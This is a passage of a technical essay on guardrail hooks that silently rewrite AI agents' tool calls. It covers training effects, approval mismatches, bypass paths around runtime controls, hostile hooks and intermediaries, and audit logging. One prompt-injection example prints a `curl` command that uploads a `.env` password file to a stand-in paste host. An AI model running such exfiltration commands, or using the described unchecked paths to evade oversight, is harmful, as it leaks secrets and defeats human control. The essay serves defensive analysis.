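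In the deployment example, crediting the executed action protects the value of deploying when action values are stored in a table, but the same approach can disrupt an algorithm that adjusts a neural network on the assumption that the network chose the action. The robotics results also depend on a safety check that can prove in advance which actions are safe, and no hook can do that for arbitrary shell commands.

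### Does this carry over to language-model agents?

Developers commonly train language models with policy-gradient methods, which don't keep a table of values. These methods make the text the model produced more likely if the attempt scored well, and less likely if it scored badly. In the simplest version, the training code changes the weights in this direction:

```text
∇J = E[ R · ∇ log π(proposed call) ]
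```

*J* is the average reward, *R* is the reward of one attempt, and ∇ indicates the change in weights that increases a quantity fastest. A hook affects *R* but not the rest of the formula, as long as its decision depends only on the call and the situation. Training therefore pushes the model towards whatever earns the most reward with the guardrail in place. The formula implies that a language-model agent that trains on its own proposed calls should behave more like the evolution strategy than like Q-learning.

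A small batch shows the effect. GRPO (group relative policy optimization), a relative of PPO, has the model attempt the same task several times and reinforces the attempts that beat the group's average. Suppose four attempts at the release earn these rewards:

| Proposed action | Executed action | Reward | Compared with the average of 5.5 |
| :- | :- | :- | :- |
| Deploy | Deploy | 10 | +4.5 |
| Deploy | Dry run | 0 | −5.5 |
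| Hand over | Hand over | 6 | +0.5 |
| Hand over | Hand over | 6 | +0.5 |

The model wrote the same command in both deployments, so the two deployments' effects on that command add up to −1, while handing over gains 1. GRPO also scales the differences by how widely the rewards vary, which doesn't change their signs.

The developer could store the executed command instead, but that would train the model on text it didn't write, which is the mismatch that hurt PPO in the robotics tests. The developer could also leave rewritten attempts out of the data, but Orseau and Armstrong warn that removing interrupted histories is likely to introduce a bias. For example, if a hook rewrites only risky deployments, the remaining data contain only easy ones, and the agent learns that deploying is safer than it is.

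These predictions still need testing on real agents. Langlois and Everitt tested REINFORCE, a basic policy-gradient method, in an environment with three levers that gave rewards of 1, 0 and −1. The guardrail favoured whichever levers the policy gave the lowest probability. REINFORCE ended with an average reward of −0.54, the lowest of five algorithms, while the evolution strategy reached 0.55. Langlois and Everitt left the explanation to future work. The formula above doesn't cover this guardrail, which responded to the policy's probabilities and not to a single call, but the result is a reason not to assume that every algorithm adapts well to every kind of rewrite.

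### Reliance on the guardrail

A guardrail that silently corrects an agent's mistakes during training can prevent the agent from learning to avoid them. Suppose the agent proposes `git push --force`, a hook changes it to `git push --force-with-lease`, and the push succeeds. If the code credits the proposed command, training reinforces a command that could overwrite a colleague's work, and the agent never experiences the consequences of running it.

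The habit does no damage while the hook works, but it can if the operator uses the model in another product without the hook, or if the hook crashes and the harness runs the original command. Langlois and Everitt raise the same concern about a self-driving car, which shouldn't learn to depend on a supervisor that keeps it on the road only during training.

Crediting the executed command would help here because it would reinforce `--force-with-lease`. With the forced dry run, though, it would preserve the agent's preference for deploying. Which command to credit depends on whether the hook supplies a command the agent should learn or only cancels one it should stop proposing. Penalising each intervention discourages the original command in both cases, but may also teach the agent to find commands the hook doesn't recognise.

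A related experiment on language models used a text instruction as the guardrail. Latif, Dailey and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluation and Restoration of Safety in Reasoning-Tuned LLMs*, trained a small reasoning model to refuse harmful requests and help with harmless ones. During training, a safety instruction in the prompt told the model to assess each request first. This was meant to produce enough safe answers to learn from, because the algorithm has nothing to reinforce if the model always answers a difficult prompt unsafely. The researchers then tested the model without the instruction.

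Without the instruction, the trained model gave fewer unsafe responses than it had before training, and it largely kept its accuracy on mathematics problems. Training with a guardrail therefore doesn't always make a model rely on it. Latif and colleagues obtained this result with evolution strategies on a single model, and they leave open how widely it holds. Unlike a hook, their guardrail influenced what the model wrote and didn't repair unsafe answers afterwards, so the reward scored the model's own words. The model could also read the guardrail, which an agent can't do with a silent hook.

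Developers can measure reliance on an action guardrail in a similar way, by running the trained agent in a disposable copy of the environment with the hook switched off and counting how often it proposes commands that the hook would have changed. Counting proposals matters because, with the hook on, the executed commands would look equally safe whether the agent had learned the rule or relied entirely on the hook.

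### Doubt about whether actions are real

If guardrails silently turn many of an agent's commands into dry runs during training, the agent may also learn that its commands often have no effect. That expectation would be correct in training, but dangerous if the agent carried it into work where every command takes effect.

Such doubt could be useful. If the reward depends on whether the service is actually running, an agent that checks the service after each deployment will score higher than one that trusts the success message. Training would then teach agents to verify results routinely, which they need to do when they can't see that a guardrail has rewritten their calls.

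It could also make the agent careless. Suppose a risky shortcut earns 2 points from a grader whether or not the commands are real, and does 10 points of damage only if they are. An agent that treats the commands as real expects a net loss of 8 points and avoids the shortcut. An agent that puts the chance of a dry run at 90% expects only 1 point of damage, so it takes the shortcut. The doubt changes the agent's choice because the shortcut earns its 2 points even in a dry run. If a dry run cancelled the gain as well as the damage, the shortcut would be a bad choice at any level of doubt.

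A mistaken belief that actions aren't real has already contributed to harm. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed that Claude models had gained unauthorised access to three organisations' real systems during tests. According to Help Net Security's *Anthropic's Claude breached three companies during security tests* (2026), the prompt told the models that they had no internet access, but a configuration error had left the connection open. Financial Express' *How Anthropic’s Claude AI ‘gained unauthorised access’ to 3 organisations* quotes Anthropic as writing that in most cases the models had held "a false belief about whether the environment was real".

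The reported cause of the incidents was a wrong statement in the prompt and a faulty test setup, not rewritten calls. The incidents are evidence that such a belief can be dangerous, but they don't show whether training with silent rewrites would produce one. If it did, the belief would be harder to correct than a false sentence in a prompt, because the developer would have to train it out of the model.

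## Does an approval cover the command that runs?

Approvals have the same weakness as rewards, because a judgement about the proposed command may not fit the one that runs. Suppose a user tells an agent that it may force-push its work to the branch `login-fix`. The agent proposes the command and a reviewer approves it. A hook that keeps agents' work separate from people's then changes the destination:

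```text
proposed:  git push --force origin login-fix
approved:  git push --force origin login-fix
executed:  git push --force origin login-fix:agent/login-fix
```

The prefix protects people's branches, but another agent may already have stored work in `agent/login-fix`, which the forced push would overwrite. Nobody reviewed this push, because the reviewer had approved a different command that never ran.

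### Checking one command and running another

Programmers call this kind of flaw time-of-check to time-of-use. In a textbook example, a program checks that a user may write to a file and then opens the file by name. If the name starts pointing to a different file between the two steps, the program writes to a file it never checked.

An attacker who exploits this flaw in an operating system usually has to get the timing right, because the gap between check and use lasts a fraction of a second. A rewriting hook doesn't depend on timing, because the harness runs it between approval and execution every time. But the harness's designer controls that order and can move the review after the hook.

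Write *a* for the proposed action, g(a) for the action the hook turns it into, and A for the set of actions the reviewer would approve. Approvals carry over to the executed action only if the hook never takes an approved action out of the set:

```text
for every a:   if a ∈ A, then g(a) ∈ A
```

A hook that only adds `--dry-run` to pushes probably meets this condition, since a reviewer who accepts a push would rarely object to a dry run. The branch hook doesn't meet it, and its author would struggle to check, because A can depend on the conversation. According to Anthropic's guide to permission modes, a user in Claude Code's auto mode can clear a blocked force push only by naming specifics such as the branch. A hook that reads only the command can't determine which branch the user named.

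Even an unchanged command can do something its reviewer didn't expect. At the start of a session, a hook can store environment settings, which Claude Code then runs as shell code before every Bash command. Those settings can determine which program `git` runs, so the same approved text can have different effects in two sessions. Auto mode guards against a related problem by blocking a deletion such as `rm -rf "$VAR"` if the conversation doesn't show what the variable contains. It can lift the block once Claude writes out the actual path.

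Verdicts can also come too late. Anthropic warns that if a hook script exits and leaves its decision to a background process, a denial that the process prints after Claude Code has stopped reading doesn't block the call. Claude Code does guard against stale approvals in auto mode. If the user switches permission modes while a check is pending, it discards any verdict that the new mode wouldn't have requested.

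### Where the review can go

| Order | What the approval covers | Main drawback |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Review, rewrite, run | The command the model wrote | Nobody has reviewed the command that runs |
| Rewrite, review, run | The command that runs, if nothing changes it later | The reviewer may not learn what the model tried to do |
| Review, rewrite, review again, run | The command that runs | The second review takes time, and any further change needs another |
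| The reviewer rewrites, then the command runs | The reviewer's own version | Nobody else checks the reviewer's edit |

Reviewing a command before the hook runs can also block commands that the hook would have made acceptable. Auto mode blocks forced pushes by default. A reviewer who saw only `git push --force` might refuse it, even though a hook was about to change it to the safer `--force-with-lease`.

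Rewriting a command before the review instead hides what the agent tried to run. Auto mode goes back to asking the user after it blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session. If a hook turned every push into a dry run before the review, an agent could try to publish 20 times, and the reviewer would see 20 harmless dry runs and have no reason to block them. A reviewer who sees both the original and the rewritten command has more to read, but can judge the command that will run and still notice what the agent keeps attempting.

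None of these orders helps if a gateway outside the harness changes the call after the harness sends it. The approval then covers only the command the harness sent, so the gateway's operator has to check the version the gateway forwards.

### How auto mode treats a changed call

According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, terminal and VS Code sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans start in auto mode by default. Many developers therefore depend on a classifier model they didn't choose to review actions in their place.

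By default, the review now happens on a server. *Claude Code Auto Mode*, a page on a personal website, dates that change to version 2.1.278, released on 19 September 2026. The verdict comes back with the model's response, and hooks run afterwards on the developer's computer, so any rewrite by a hook happens after the review.

Anthropic's documentation of November 2026 describes what happens when a hook changes a call without returning a verdict of its own:

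1. Claude writes a call, and the server reviews it.
2. The hook returns a changed input.
3. Claude Code can deny the changed call, because the server reviewed a different one. In terminal and VS Code sessions with a direct connection to Anthropic's API, the denial includes the words "a hook changed this call's input after auto mode reviewed it".
4. Claude can then issue the changed call itself, which sends it to the server for review.
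5. If Claude repeats the changed input exactly in its next response, the hook runs again. It can still deny the call or have Claude Code ask the user, but Claude Code drops any further change.

The command that runs is then the one the server reviewed. Because the model wrote the final version itself, the transcript also contains that command, and the rewrite is no longer silent. This takes an extra round of the loop, which rewriting was supposed to avoid.

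Dropping further changes also prevents an endless cycle. Otherwise, the sample hook that adds `/sandbox` to the start of file paths would add it again to the resubmitted call, and the server would have to review a third version.

Resubmission doesn't suit a guardrail that swaps a placeholder for a secret key just before the command runs, because the model would need the real key to repeat the changed input exactly.

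The exceptions cover the most common kind of rewrite. In sessions that show the explanatory text, a hook that runs a command can change shell commands, file edits, file writes and notebook edits without triggering this denial, provided the hook comes from a settings file the operator wrote or from a plugin's hooks file. The denial can still appear if a hook changed an earlier call in the same response, or if the agent asks to run a Bash command outside the sandbox. The branch hook would therefore not normally trigger the denial, even though the server had reviewed a push to a different branch.

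The operator's permission rules still apply, but a rule that permits pushes in general wouldn't stop a push to the wrong branch. The description of the exception doesn't mention a new review by the classifier. An operator who wants the changed command reviewed can have the hook return "ask", which normally shows it to a person.

A hook that returns "allow" also avoids the mismatch, by approving its own rewrite. The hook that forces `git push` into a dry run does this. No separate reviewer has checked the new command, so the approval is only as reliable as the hook's code.

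Anthropic warns that in other sessions Claude Code can deny a changed call without the explanatory text. It treats the call as if the server gave no verdict, and it can stop the turn after ten consecutive responses without a verdict. A model that isn't given the reason may keep proposing the original command, which the hook changes every time.

Operators can also turn off the server's review and have Claude Code send its own requests to the classifier. Claude Code could send such a request after the hook runs, so the verdict could cover the changed command. The server's verdict can't cover that command because it arrives with the model's response, before the hook runs.

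A rewrite can also mislead the classifier about later calls. The requests that Claude Code sends to the classifier include the user's messages and most of Claude's tool calls, and by default the classifier lets Claude delete jobs that it created earlier in the session. Suppose Claude tries to create a job called `nightly`, but a hook turns the command into a local dry run that never contacts the server. If a colleague already has a job with that name, Claude may later delete it, thinking the job is its own. A classifier that reads Claude's original call has good reason to approve the deletion, which then runs as approved even though the original command never ran.

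### Which version does a person see?

When a Claude Code hook returns "ask", the permission prompt shows the changed command with a label that identifies the hook's source as a settings file, a named plugin or a skill. The prompt doesn't show which words the hook changed, so a developer who sees `login-fix:agent/login-fix` might assume that the agent chose that destination.

Applications built on the Agent SDK can rewrite a call before or after the user approves it. According to Anthropic, a call passes through hooks, "deny" rules, "ask" rules, the permission mode and "allow" rules before it reaches the application's permission callback. Any changes made by hooks are therefore in place before the application asks for approval. The callback receives the tool's name and input, which Anthropic suggests displaying to the user, and it can return a different input after the user says yes.

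If such an application displayed `rm -rf /tmp/build` and then redirected the path to the sandbox, the user would have approved a deletion that never happened. The developer can avoid this by rewriting the command before displaying it. In LangChain, the reviewer edits the call directly, so the approved and executed versions match.

Claude Code reserves some approvals for people. A hook's "allow" can't approve the removal of certain critical paths. It also can't skip the prompt for an outside tool whose server requires user interaction. This applies even if the hook supplies a changed input, because Claude Code can't confirm that the hook collected the answer from a user.

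Bugs can prevent the approval prompt from appearing. On Cursor's forum, *preToolUse hook updated_input silently discarded for Write tool (file creation/edit)* describes a hook that replaced a new file's text and asked for approval, but Cursor discarded the change and showed no prompt. In *Hooks*, a thread on the same forum about version 2.4.21, a reply acknowledged that "ask" no longer worked for shell commands and MCP calls, though "allow" and "deny" still worked. The reply recommended denying critical operations until the bug was fixed.

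A bug report reproduced on Good First Issue describes a similar problem with RTK in Claude Code. RTK's hook returned a changed command without a verdict and relied on Claude Code to apply the change and ask the user about it. But the output came back in its ordinary format, so the user concluded that the original command had run.

These reports come from users of particular versions, and the faults may since have been fixed. An operator can test for them by having the hook change a harmless command, then checking that the prompt appears and that the changed version runs.

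### Actions that no reviewer sees

Even a well-placed review covers only the actions that pass through it, so it misses whatever an approved script does once it runs. In *guardscope*, Toyoda, Leung and U (2026) measured the share of an agent's activity that runtime controls check.

They listed 15 paths by which an agent's action can take effect, and eight designs for a system with or without a control. An action is "checked" if it crosses the control, "bypassed" if it takes effect without doing so, and "prevented" if something outside the policy, such as a network block, stops it. The table gives the number of paths that four of the designs should always check, according to their analysis:

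| Where the control sits | Paths checked, out of 15 | What it can inspect |
| :- | :- | :- |
| A gateway for tool servers reached over HTTP | 1 | The full request |
| A gateway for all tool servers, with direct network access blocked | 3 | The full request |
| The harness's own permission checks | 5 | The tool's name, its arguments and the session |
| The operating system's kernel | 13 | File paths, network addresses and process history, but not the tool or session |

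Five of the paths bypass every design outside the kernel. They include background processes that keep running after the call that started them ends and jobs the agent hands to a scheduler. Adding a gateway to the harness's own checks gives a reviewer more detail but doesn't cover these five paths.

The researchers then tested real controls with a fixed set of 15 actions. They replayed the actions through an agent harness without a language model, so that every run was the same. A separate sensor in the kernel recorded what happened. Before each run, they issued an action that the policy had to deny, and continued only if the control refused it. Such a check would also catch a hook that fails without an error.

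A setup with permission checks in the harness and a gateway in front of the tool servers checked all seven tool calls. The other eight actions, which included direct network connections and file writes, took effect unchecked. ActPlane, a control that works in the kernel, checked seven of those eight actions, one of which it blocked, but missed all seven tool calls. Only one of the 15 actions, a network message of a type that ActPlane doesn't monitor, escaped both setups.

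The test actions used only four of the 15 paths, so the results for the other 11 come from analysis. "Checked" doesn't mean that the control made the right decision or that the action ran in the form that was checked, since an action can be rewritten afterward.

### When the change is hostile

A model can't distinguish a hostile rewrite from a protective one if it isn't notified of the change, so people and software outside the model have to establish who may change its tool calls.

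A hostile change could come from a hook. Plugins, skills and a project's settings can all contain hooks for Claude Code, so a developer who installs a plugin or opens someone else's project may receive code that alters commands. Once the user or Claude invokes a skill, its hooks normally keep running for the rest of the session, even on unrelated turns. Auto mode's exception for command hooks also applies to those in a plugin's hooks file, whether the plugin is careful or malicious.

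A service between the harness and the model's provider could also change a tool call in the model's reply. Some developers use such intermediaries to reach several companies' models through one account. The harness has an encrypted connection to the intermediary, which has a separate one to the provider, so the intermediary can read and alter the text that passes between them. The harness would receive an altered call as though the model had written it.

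Even when the review happens in the right order, it can fail to protect the user. The person sees and approves the altered command, and the harness runs exactly that command, but the model proposed something else. The harness also stores the altered call in the transcript, so the model may treat it as its own on the next turn.

Intermediaries can also interfere with the review. If a gateway drops the request for a server review, Claude Code falls back to its own classifier requests. If the gateway makes the results unreadable, Claude Code denies the action.

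### Defences against unauthorised changes

Operators can start by limiting who may install hooks. An administrator can use the setting `allowManagedHooksOnly` to block hooks from users, projects and plugins, except plugins the administrator has required. A second setting restricts which web addresses hooks may contact. This matters because a hook that gets its decision from a remote service can start returning different rewrites without any change on the developer's computer.

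These controls move trust to the administrator but don't make rewrites visible. A managed hook can rewrite a command as silently as a hostile one, and a mistake in it affects everyone in the organisation.

For developers without an administrator, Claude Code has a workspace trust dialog that asks whether they trust a folder. Hooks in a project's subagent files run only after the developer accepts the dialog. But Anthropic says that in a non-interactive run, Claude Code registers hooks in a project's skills when someone invokes the skill, even if the developer hasn't trusted the folder. Automated jobs that process unfamiliar code therefore need another safeguard, such as an isolated machine without valuable credentials.

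Developers can also turn off all hooks in their user settings, but a project's settings can turn them back on. A setting passed on the command line overrides the project's for that run. Before starting work, a developer can use the `/hooks` menu to see each configured hook's source and the full text of what it runs. If a hook calls a remote service, that text doesn't include the code that chooses the rewrite.

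None of these settings protects against an intermediary, but a digital signature could. The model's provider would sign each tool call with a private key, and the harness would verify the signature with the matching public key. If an intermediary changed even one character, the verification would fail, and the intermediary couldn't produce a new signature without the private key.

But a hook runs after the harness has received the call, so a valid signature on the model's original doesn't cover the hook's version. To close that gap, the harness can attach the approval to a fingerprint of the exact input, which a standard function computes from the text:

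```text
approved:      git push --force origin login-fix                    → 7c1e…
about to run:  git push --force origin login-fix:agent/login-fix    → 91b4…
result:        the fingerprints differ, so the harness asks for a new approval
```

The fingerprint should also cover the tool's name, the working directory and the call's identifier. Otherwise someone could reuse an approval to run the same text in a different directory or at a later time. Even then, editing the script doesn't change the fingerprint of `bash deploy.sh` unless the harness includes the script's contents in it.

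Operators can also compare the call the harness sent with what the computer did. Toyoda and colleagues do this by matching each control's records against the kernel's, using identifiers passed along with the tool calls. The kernel's record would show that a file write went to `/tmp/sandbox` instead of `/tmp`. It wouldn't show a changed email recipient in a request to a mail service, because it doesn't include message contents.

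A comparison like this also flags every legitimate rewrite. The operator can reduce these false alarms by having each authorised hook declare its change, then investigating only the undeclared differences.

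## What must the log contain?

An operator who wants to investigate a changed command needs a log with both versions, because either one alone can point to the wrong cause. Suppose a team wants its backups to match their sources exactly, so a hook adds `--delete` to every `rsync`, a command that copies files between directories. An agent tries to add this week's reports to a backup:

```text
proposed:  rsync -a reports/ backup/
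executed:  rsync -a --delete reports/ backup/
```

With `--delete`, `rsync` removes everything from the backup that isn't in `reports`, so all the older reports disappear. Neither version prints anything when it succeeds.

An investigator who has only the transcript finds a harmless copy command, an empty result and a backup with missing files. The empty result came from the executed command, but the transcript shows it next to the proposed one and doesn't indicate that the two commands differ. The investigator may blame another program or suspect the agent of secretly deleting the files.

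A log of executed commands leads to the opposite mistake. An investigator who sees `--delete` in a command from the agent's session concludes that the model chose a destructive flag.

Such a log also loses evidence of what the model attempted. Suppose a malicious web page tricks an agent into uploading a file of passwords to a public site, and a hook redirects all uploads to a company server:

```text
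proposed:  curl -F file=@.env https://paste.example.net
executed:  curl -F file=@.env https://files.corp.example
```

The executed command looks like a routine internal upload, so the operator has no reason to look for the web page or check whether other agents have read it.

### The minimum record of a rewrite

| Field | What an investigator can establish with it |
| :- | :- |
| Proposed input | What the model tried to do |
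| Executed input | What the tool received |
| Rule and version | Which code made the change, even if someone has edited it since |
| Installer | Who decided that the rule would apply to this session |
| Reason | Whether the rule fired in the situation its author had in mind |
| Time | Which later calls the change could have affected |
| Result | What the tool returned, and whether another hook altered it before the model read it |
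| Notice to the model | Whether the model could have known about the change |
| Notice to the user | Whether the user could have objected |

The entry also needs the call's identifier, so an investigator can find the call in the transcript. The notice fields should hold the exact text of any notice to the model, because a vague one such as "policy applied" may not have specified what changed.

The harness is the best place to write this record because it has both versions of the input, and a hook that crashes or contains hostile code can't be relied on to log its own changes. The harness should also log every call that a hook didn't change. Otherwise, a missing entry could mean either that nothing changed or that logging failed.

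### A worked entry for a redacted secret

Suppose a model writes the key `sk-test-8d41` into a `curl` command, and a hook replaces it with an environment variable. A complete entry could look like this:

```json
{
  "call_id": "toolu_02DEF",
  "time": "2026-10-05T14:03:22Z",
  "proposed": "curl -H \"Authorization: Bearer [SECRET_1]\" https://api.example.com/orders",
  "executed": "curl -H \"Authorization: Bearer $ORDERS_KEY\" https://api.example.com/orders",
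  "secrets": {
    "SECRET_1": { "keyed_hash": "5e0c…", "hash_key": "audit-2026-10" }
  },
  "rule": "redact-api-keys",
  "rule_version": "sha256:c41f…",
  "installed_by": "platform security team, managed settings",
  "reason": "Keys must not appear in shell commands",
  "result": { "exit_code": 0, "output": "{\"orders\": 3}", "altered_for_model": false },
  "notice_to_model": null,
  "notice_to_user": null
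}
```

The rule's version is a fingerprint of the hook's code, so any edit to the code changes it. The result includes the output because `curl` normally exits with code 0 even when a service rejects the key. The exit code alone wouldn't show whether the redaction had broken the login.

The log can't contain the proposed command exactly as the model wrote it, because anyone with access to the log could then read the key. A **placeholder** such as `[SECRET_1]` keeps the key out of the log. But if every session numbers its own placeholders, `[SECRET_1]` may stand for different keys in different sessions, and an investigator can't check which key it replaced in each one.

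Storing an ordinary hash beside the placeholder would identify the key, but it may also reveal it. A hash function such as SHA-256 turns any text into a fixed-length code and can't be run backwards, but anyone who can read the log can hash a guess and compare the result. If an attacker knows that a key consists of `sk-test-` and four hexadecimal digits, a laptop can try all 16⁴ = 65,536 possibilities in about a second. Anthropic's Claude Code includes a hash of an administrator's settings in its monitoring data only if the organisation opts in, because someone could recover a short policy by hashing guesses. Real keys are usually long and random enough to resist guessing, but passwords that people choose often aren't.

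A **keyed hash** prevents this attack by mixing in a second secret, here called `audit-2026-10`, which the operator stores away from the log. An attacker who steals only the log can't test guesses. While the second secret stays the same, a given key always produces the same code, so an investigator can find every call that contained that key. If a key turns up on a public website, the investigator can compute its code and search the log for that code. Replacing the second secret changes the code for each key, so old and new entries no longer match. The entry therefore names the secret it used.

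An **encrypted field** keeps the original text, which an investigator can read with a decryption key. This helps when the hook replaces something by mistake, such as the 40-character identifier of a code change that it misclassifies as a password. A keyed hash would only let the investigator confirm a guess about the original text. The risk is that anyone who steals the decryption key can read every secret in the log.

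| Method | Can an investigator recover the text? | Can an investigator find the same secret elsewhere? | Main risk |
| :- | :- | :- | :- |
| Placeholder | No | Only if the numbering is consistent across sessions | The log can't show whether the hook redacted the right thing |
| Keyed hash | No | Yes | A thief with the hashing key can test guesses |
| Encrypted field | Yes | Only after decrypting the entries | A thief with the decryption key can read everything |

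For most operators, a placeholder with a keyed hash is the best default. An encrypted field is worth the risk while a redaction rule is new and its errors are still common.

None of these methods protects the transcript. If the harness keeps the model's original call there, the key stays in the file as plain text. Anthropic warns that prompts can also remain in the transcript on disk, even after a hook blocks them. The operator should therefore replace any key that a model has written into a command, however well the audit log protects it.

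### What Claude Code records

Claude Code spreads the parts of this record across several places, and some of them are off by default:

| Source | What it contributes | What limits it |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Transcript | The model's original call and the result the model read | Claude Code deletes it after 30 days by default |
| Debug log | A command hook's printed reply, including any changed input | Someone has to switch debug logging on |
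| Input to a hook that runs after the tool | The arguments sent to the tool, and its result | The operator has to write a hook that saves them |
| Exported events | Permission decisions, tool results and hook activity | They leave out commands unless the operator enables tool details |

To log rewrites, an operator can use a `PreToolUse` hook to save each call's original input and a `PostToolUse` hook to save the arguments that reached the tool. Both hooks receive the call's identifier, which Anthropic provides for matching the two events, so a short script can list every call whose input changed. The `PreToolUse` logging hook receives the original input even when another hook rewrites it, because Claude Code runs matching hooks in parallel. The operator also needs a `PostToolUseFailure` hook, since `PostToolUse` runs only after a tool succeeds. If the user presses Esc, Claude Code cancels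 the `PostToolUse` hooks, which leaves a gap in the log.

Claude Code can also export events through OpenTelemetry, an open standard for collecting operational data from software. Anthropic's Agent SDK exports the same data because it runs the same program. One event records the permission decision for a call, and another records the tool's result. With tool details enabled, both events contain the command. Anthropic warns that the two commands may differ if the permission decision changed the input, so comparing them can expose a rewrite. A match is weaker evidence that nothing changed, because Anthropic doesn't promise in its documentation that the decision event always contains the model's original command.

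Claude Code's log can also miss a hook's change near the end of a long script. In the field that holds a tool's full arguments, Claude Code shortens any value over 512 characters and limits the whole field to about 4,000 characters. Anthropic applies the same limits in Cowork, another of its agent products.

At the start of a session, Claude Code records whether each hook came from the user's settings, the project, an administrator or a plugin. After hooks run, it records how many succeeded, blocked the action or failed. These events don't show how many rewrites occurred, because a hook that rewrote a command and a hook that did nothing both count as successes.

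Since version 2.1.280, the same event has included the total length of the notes that hooks returned for the model and, separately, the total length of their messages for the user. If the total for the model is zero, the hooks gave it no note about a rewrite. Otherwise, the operator still has to find the text, because the note could concern something else. The event combines all the hooks that ran. Its listed attributes don't include the call's identifier, so an investigator may struggle to match it to one of several simultaneous calls.

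OpenTelemetry also has conventions for generative AI, which give data from different products common names to help operators join records from several systems. According to Anthropic's tables, Claude Code uses these conventions for the call ID, the model name, the response ID and the reason the model stopped. None of the attributes Anthropic lists under the conventions describes a changed input, so an operator who wants to export rewrites has to add their own fields.

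If a hook replaces a tool's output before the model reads it, Claude Code's telemetry still holds the original output. An investigator relying on the telemetry might conclude that the model ignored an error that it never received.

### When the screen differs from the transcript

In an interactive session, Claude Code passes each batch of finished lines to its display hook, `MessageDisplay`, and shows the text the hook returns. The transcript keeps the original text. The hook handles only the agent's own messages, so tool results appear unchanged.

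The difference between the transcript and what the user saw matters for the field that records whether the user knew about a rewrite. Suppose the model receives a note about a dry run and writes, "The push was only a rehearsal, so nothing is published yet." A hook meant to shorten messages removes that sentence from the user's screen, but the transcript still contains it. A user who later complains about not being told would be right, even though the transcript appears to prove otherwise.

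If the hook crashes or exceeds its time limit (10 seconds by default), Claude Code displays the original text and notes the failure only in debug output. A user could then see an API key that the hook normally hides, and the transcript would be the same whether the hook worked or failed. The operator also has to save the displayed text to establish what the user read.

### Tallam's evidence record

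Tallam's architecture treats an audit record as evidence for someone who may have to reconstruct events long afterwards with only some of the records. For each action *a*, Tallam defines the record as:

```text
e(a) = ⟨Π, D(a), C, R, χ, μ⟩
```

Π is the chain of people and agents who delegated the task, with the authority each one held. D(a) is the decision, including any changes to the arguments, and C lists the policy clauses that produced it. R records whether the network, identity, endpoint and data controls each carried out their part. χ links the record to related ones, and μ is a cryptographic seal that reveals later changes.

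When a rewrite causes harm, an investigator can use the full chain to see whose authority the agent was using. But the record has no separate field for whether the model or the user received a notice. It also lacks the session's state, such as whether the agent had already read confidential files, although Tallam's decision procedure depends on that state. To rerun a decision, an investigator would first have to rebuild the state from earlier records.

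Tallam also requires that partial evidence reliably limit what could have happened. If an agent was authorized to push to only two repositories and the record of one push is missing, an investigator may not know which of the two received it but can rule out any other. Each additional record can narrow the possibilities further. This reasoning fails for actions that bypass the controls, such as those of a background process that no control monitors.

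Once the system seals a record, nobody may edit it, and corrections go into new records that refer to the old one. A guardrail therefore has to redact secrets before sealing. If a secret is in an encrypted field, the operator can still make it unreadable later by destroying the decryption key, without changing the record.

Tallam tested an implementation of the policy engine's core. The evidence met the reconstruction requirement in every trial and the seal revealed tampering as designed, which shows that the code follows its specification. Each decision took less than 10 microseconds, so the engine adds almost no delay. Tallam didn't test it on a live agent benchmark, so the results don't show whether investigators could use the records to explain a real agent's mistakes.

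### What the EU AI Act requires

Some operators will also have legal duties to keep logs. Three articles of the European Union's AI Act bear on rewriting, although none of them mentions it:

- **Article 12** requires high-risk AI systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The logs must help identify situations in which the system presents a risk or has changed substantially, and must support monitoring of the system in use.
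- **Article 14** requires providers to design these systems so that people can oversee them effectively. Overseers must be able to interpret the output correctly, disregard or reverse it, and stop the system.
- **Article 26** requires deployers, the organisations that use the systems, to assign oversight to competent people. They must also keep the automatic logs under their control for at least six months, unless other law provides otherwise.

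High-risk systems include those for certain sensitive uses, such as recruitment and credit scoring, and safety components of certain regulated products. These categories usually cover an agent that filters job applications but not one that only writes code. Amendments that took effect in July 2026 postponed the duties, as the National Law Review reported in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force*. The duties now apply from 2 December 2027 to the sensitive uses and from 2 August 2028 to systems in regulated products.

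A rewrite could still matter under these articles. Suppose a recruitment agent searches for applicants with "a degree or equivalent experience", and a guardrail silently removes "or equivalent experience". An overseer who reads the original query would misinterpret the list of candidates, and a log without the executed query wouldn't help identify the risk. This is a reason to record rewrites in high-risk systems, though the Act doesn't prescribe the log's fields.

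Claude Code keeps transcripts for 30 days by default, but Article 26 requires six months, so a deployer who relied on transcripts to comply would have to extend the retention period.

### Who caused a wrong outcome?

With both versions of a command, an investigator can ask whether the harm would have happened if the proposed command had run unchanged:

| | Executed command is harmless | Executed command is harmful |
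| :- | :- | :- |
| **Proposed command was harmless** | Nothing to explain | The rewrite caused the harm |
| **Proposed command was harmful** | The rewrite prevented harm, but the model's attempt still counts against it | The rewrite failed to prevent the harm, or replaced it with another |

The deleted backup belongs in the top right cell. The model bears little responsibility, because its command would only have added files. The rule's author and the operator share the rest, in proportions that depend on what each of them knew. If the author published the hook with a clear warning that it adds `--delete`, the operator should have considered the backups before installing it. If the author slipped the flag into an update described as a minor fix, the author is mostly to blame. To tell these cases apart, the investigator needs to know the rule's version and who installed it.

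Comparing one command at a time can miss delayed harm. In the order-service example, the command that broke the service ran unchanged, so the investigator also has to check whether the model relied on the result of an earlier rewrite.

Ordinary activity logs can attribute an action to the wrong person. When a developer starts a Claude Code session, Anthropic attributes its shell commands and file edits to that developer, because Claude Code has no separate account in that session. If an administrator's hook added `--delete` to a command, the event would be logged under the name of the developer, who neither wrote nor saw the flag.

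### How unrecorded rewrites distort safety measures

The same confusion affects statistics about models. Let *h* be the share of a model's proposed calls that are harmful, *c* the share of those that the guardrail makes harmless, and *f* the share of harmless calls that it makes harmful. Then:

```text
harmful share of executed calls  =  h(1 − c) + (1 − h)f
```

Suppose a model makes 10,000 calls, of which 4% are harmful. The guardrail fixes 90% of those but damages 0.5% of the harmless ones:

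| | Calls |
| :- | :- |
| Harmful proposals | 400 |
| Harmful proposals that the guardrail fixes | 360 |
| Harmful proposals that still do harm | 40 |
| Harmless proposals that the guardrail makes harmful | 48 |
| Harmful executed calls | 88 |

An evaluator who has only the executed calls would attribute their 0.88% harm rate to the model. The model actually proposes harmful calls 4% of the time and would do far more damage in a product without the guardrail. The guardrail also caused more than half of the 88 harmful calls that were executed. A second model that runs unguarded and proposes harmful calls 1% of the time would look less safe than the first, although it proposes them a quarter as often.

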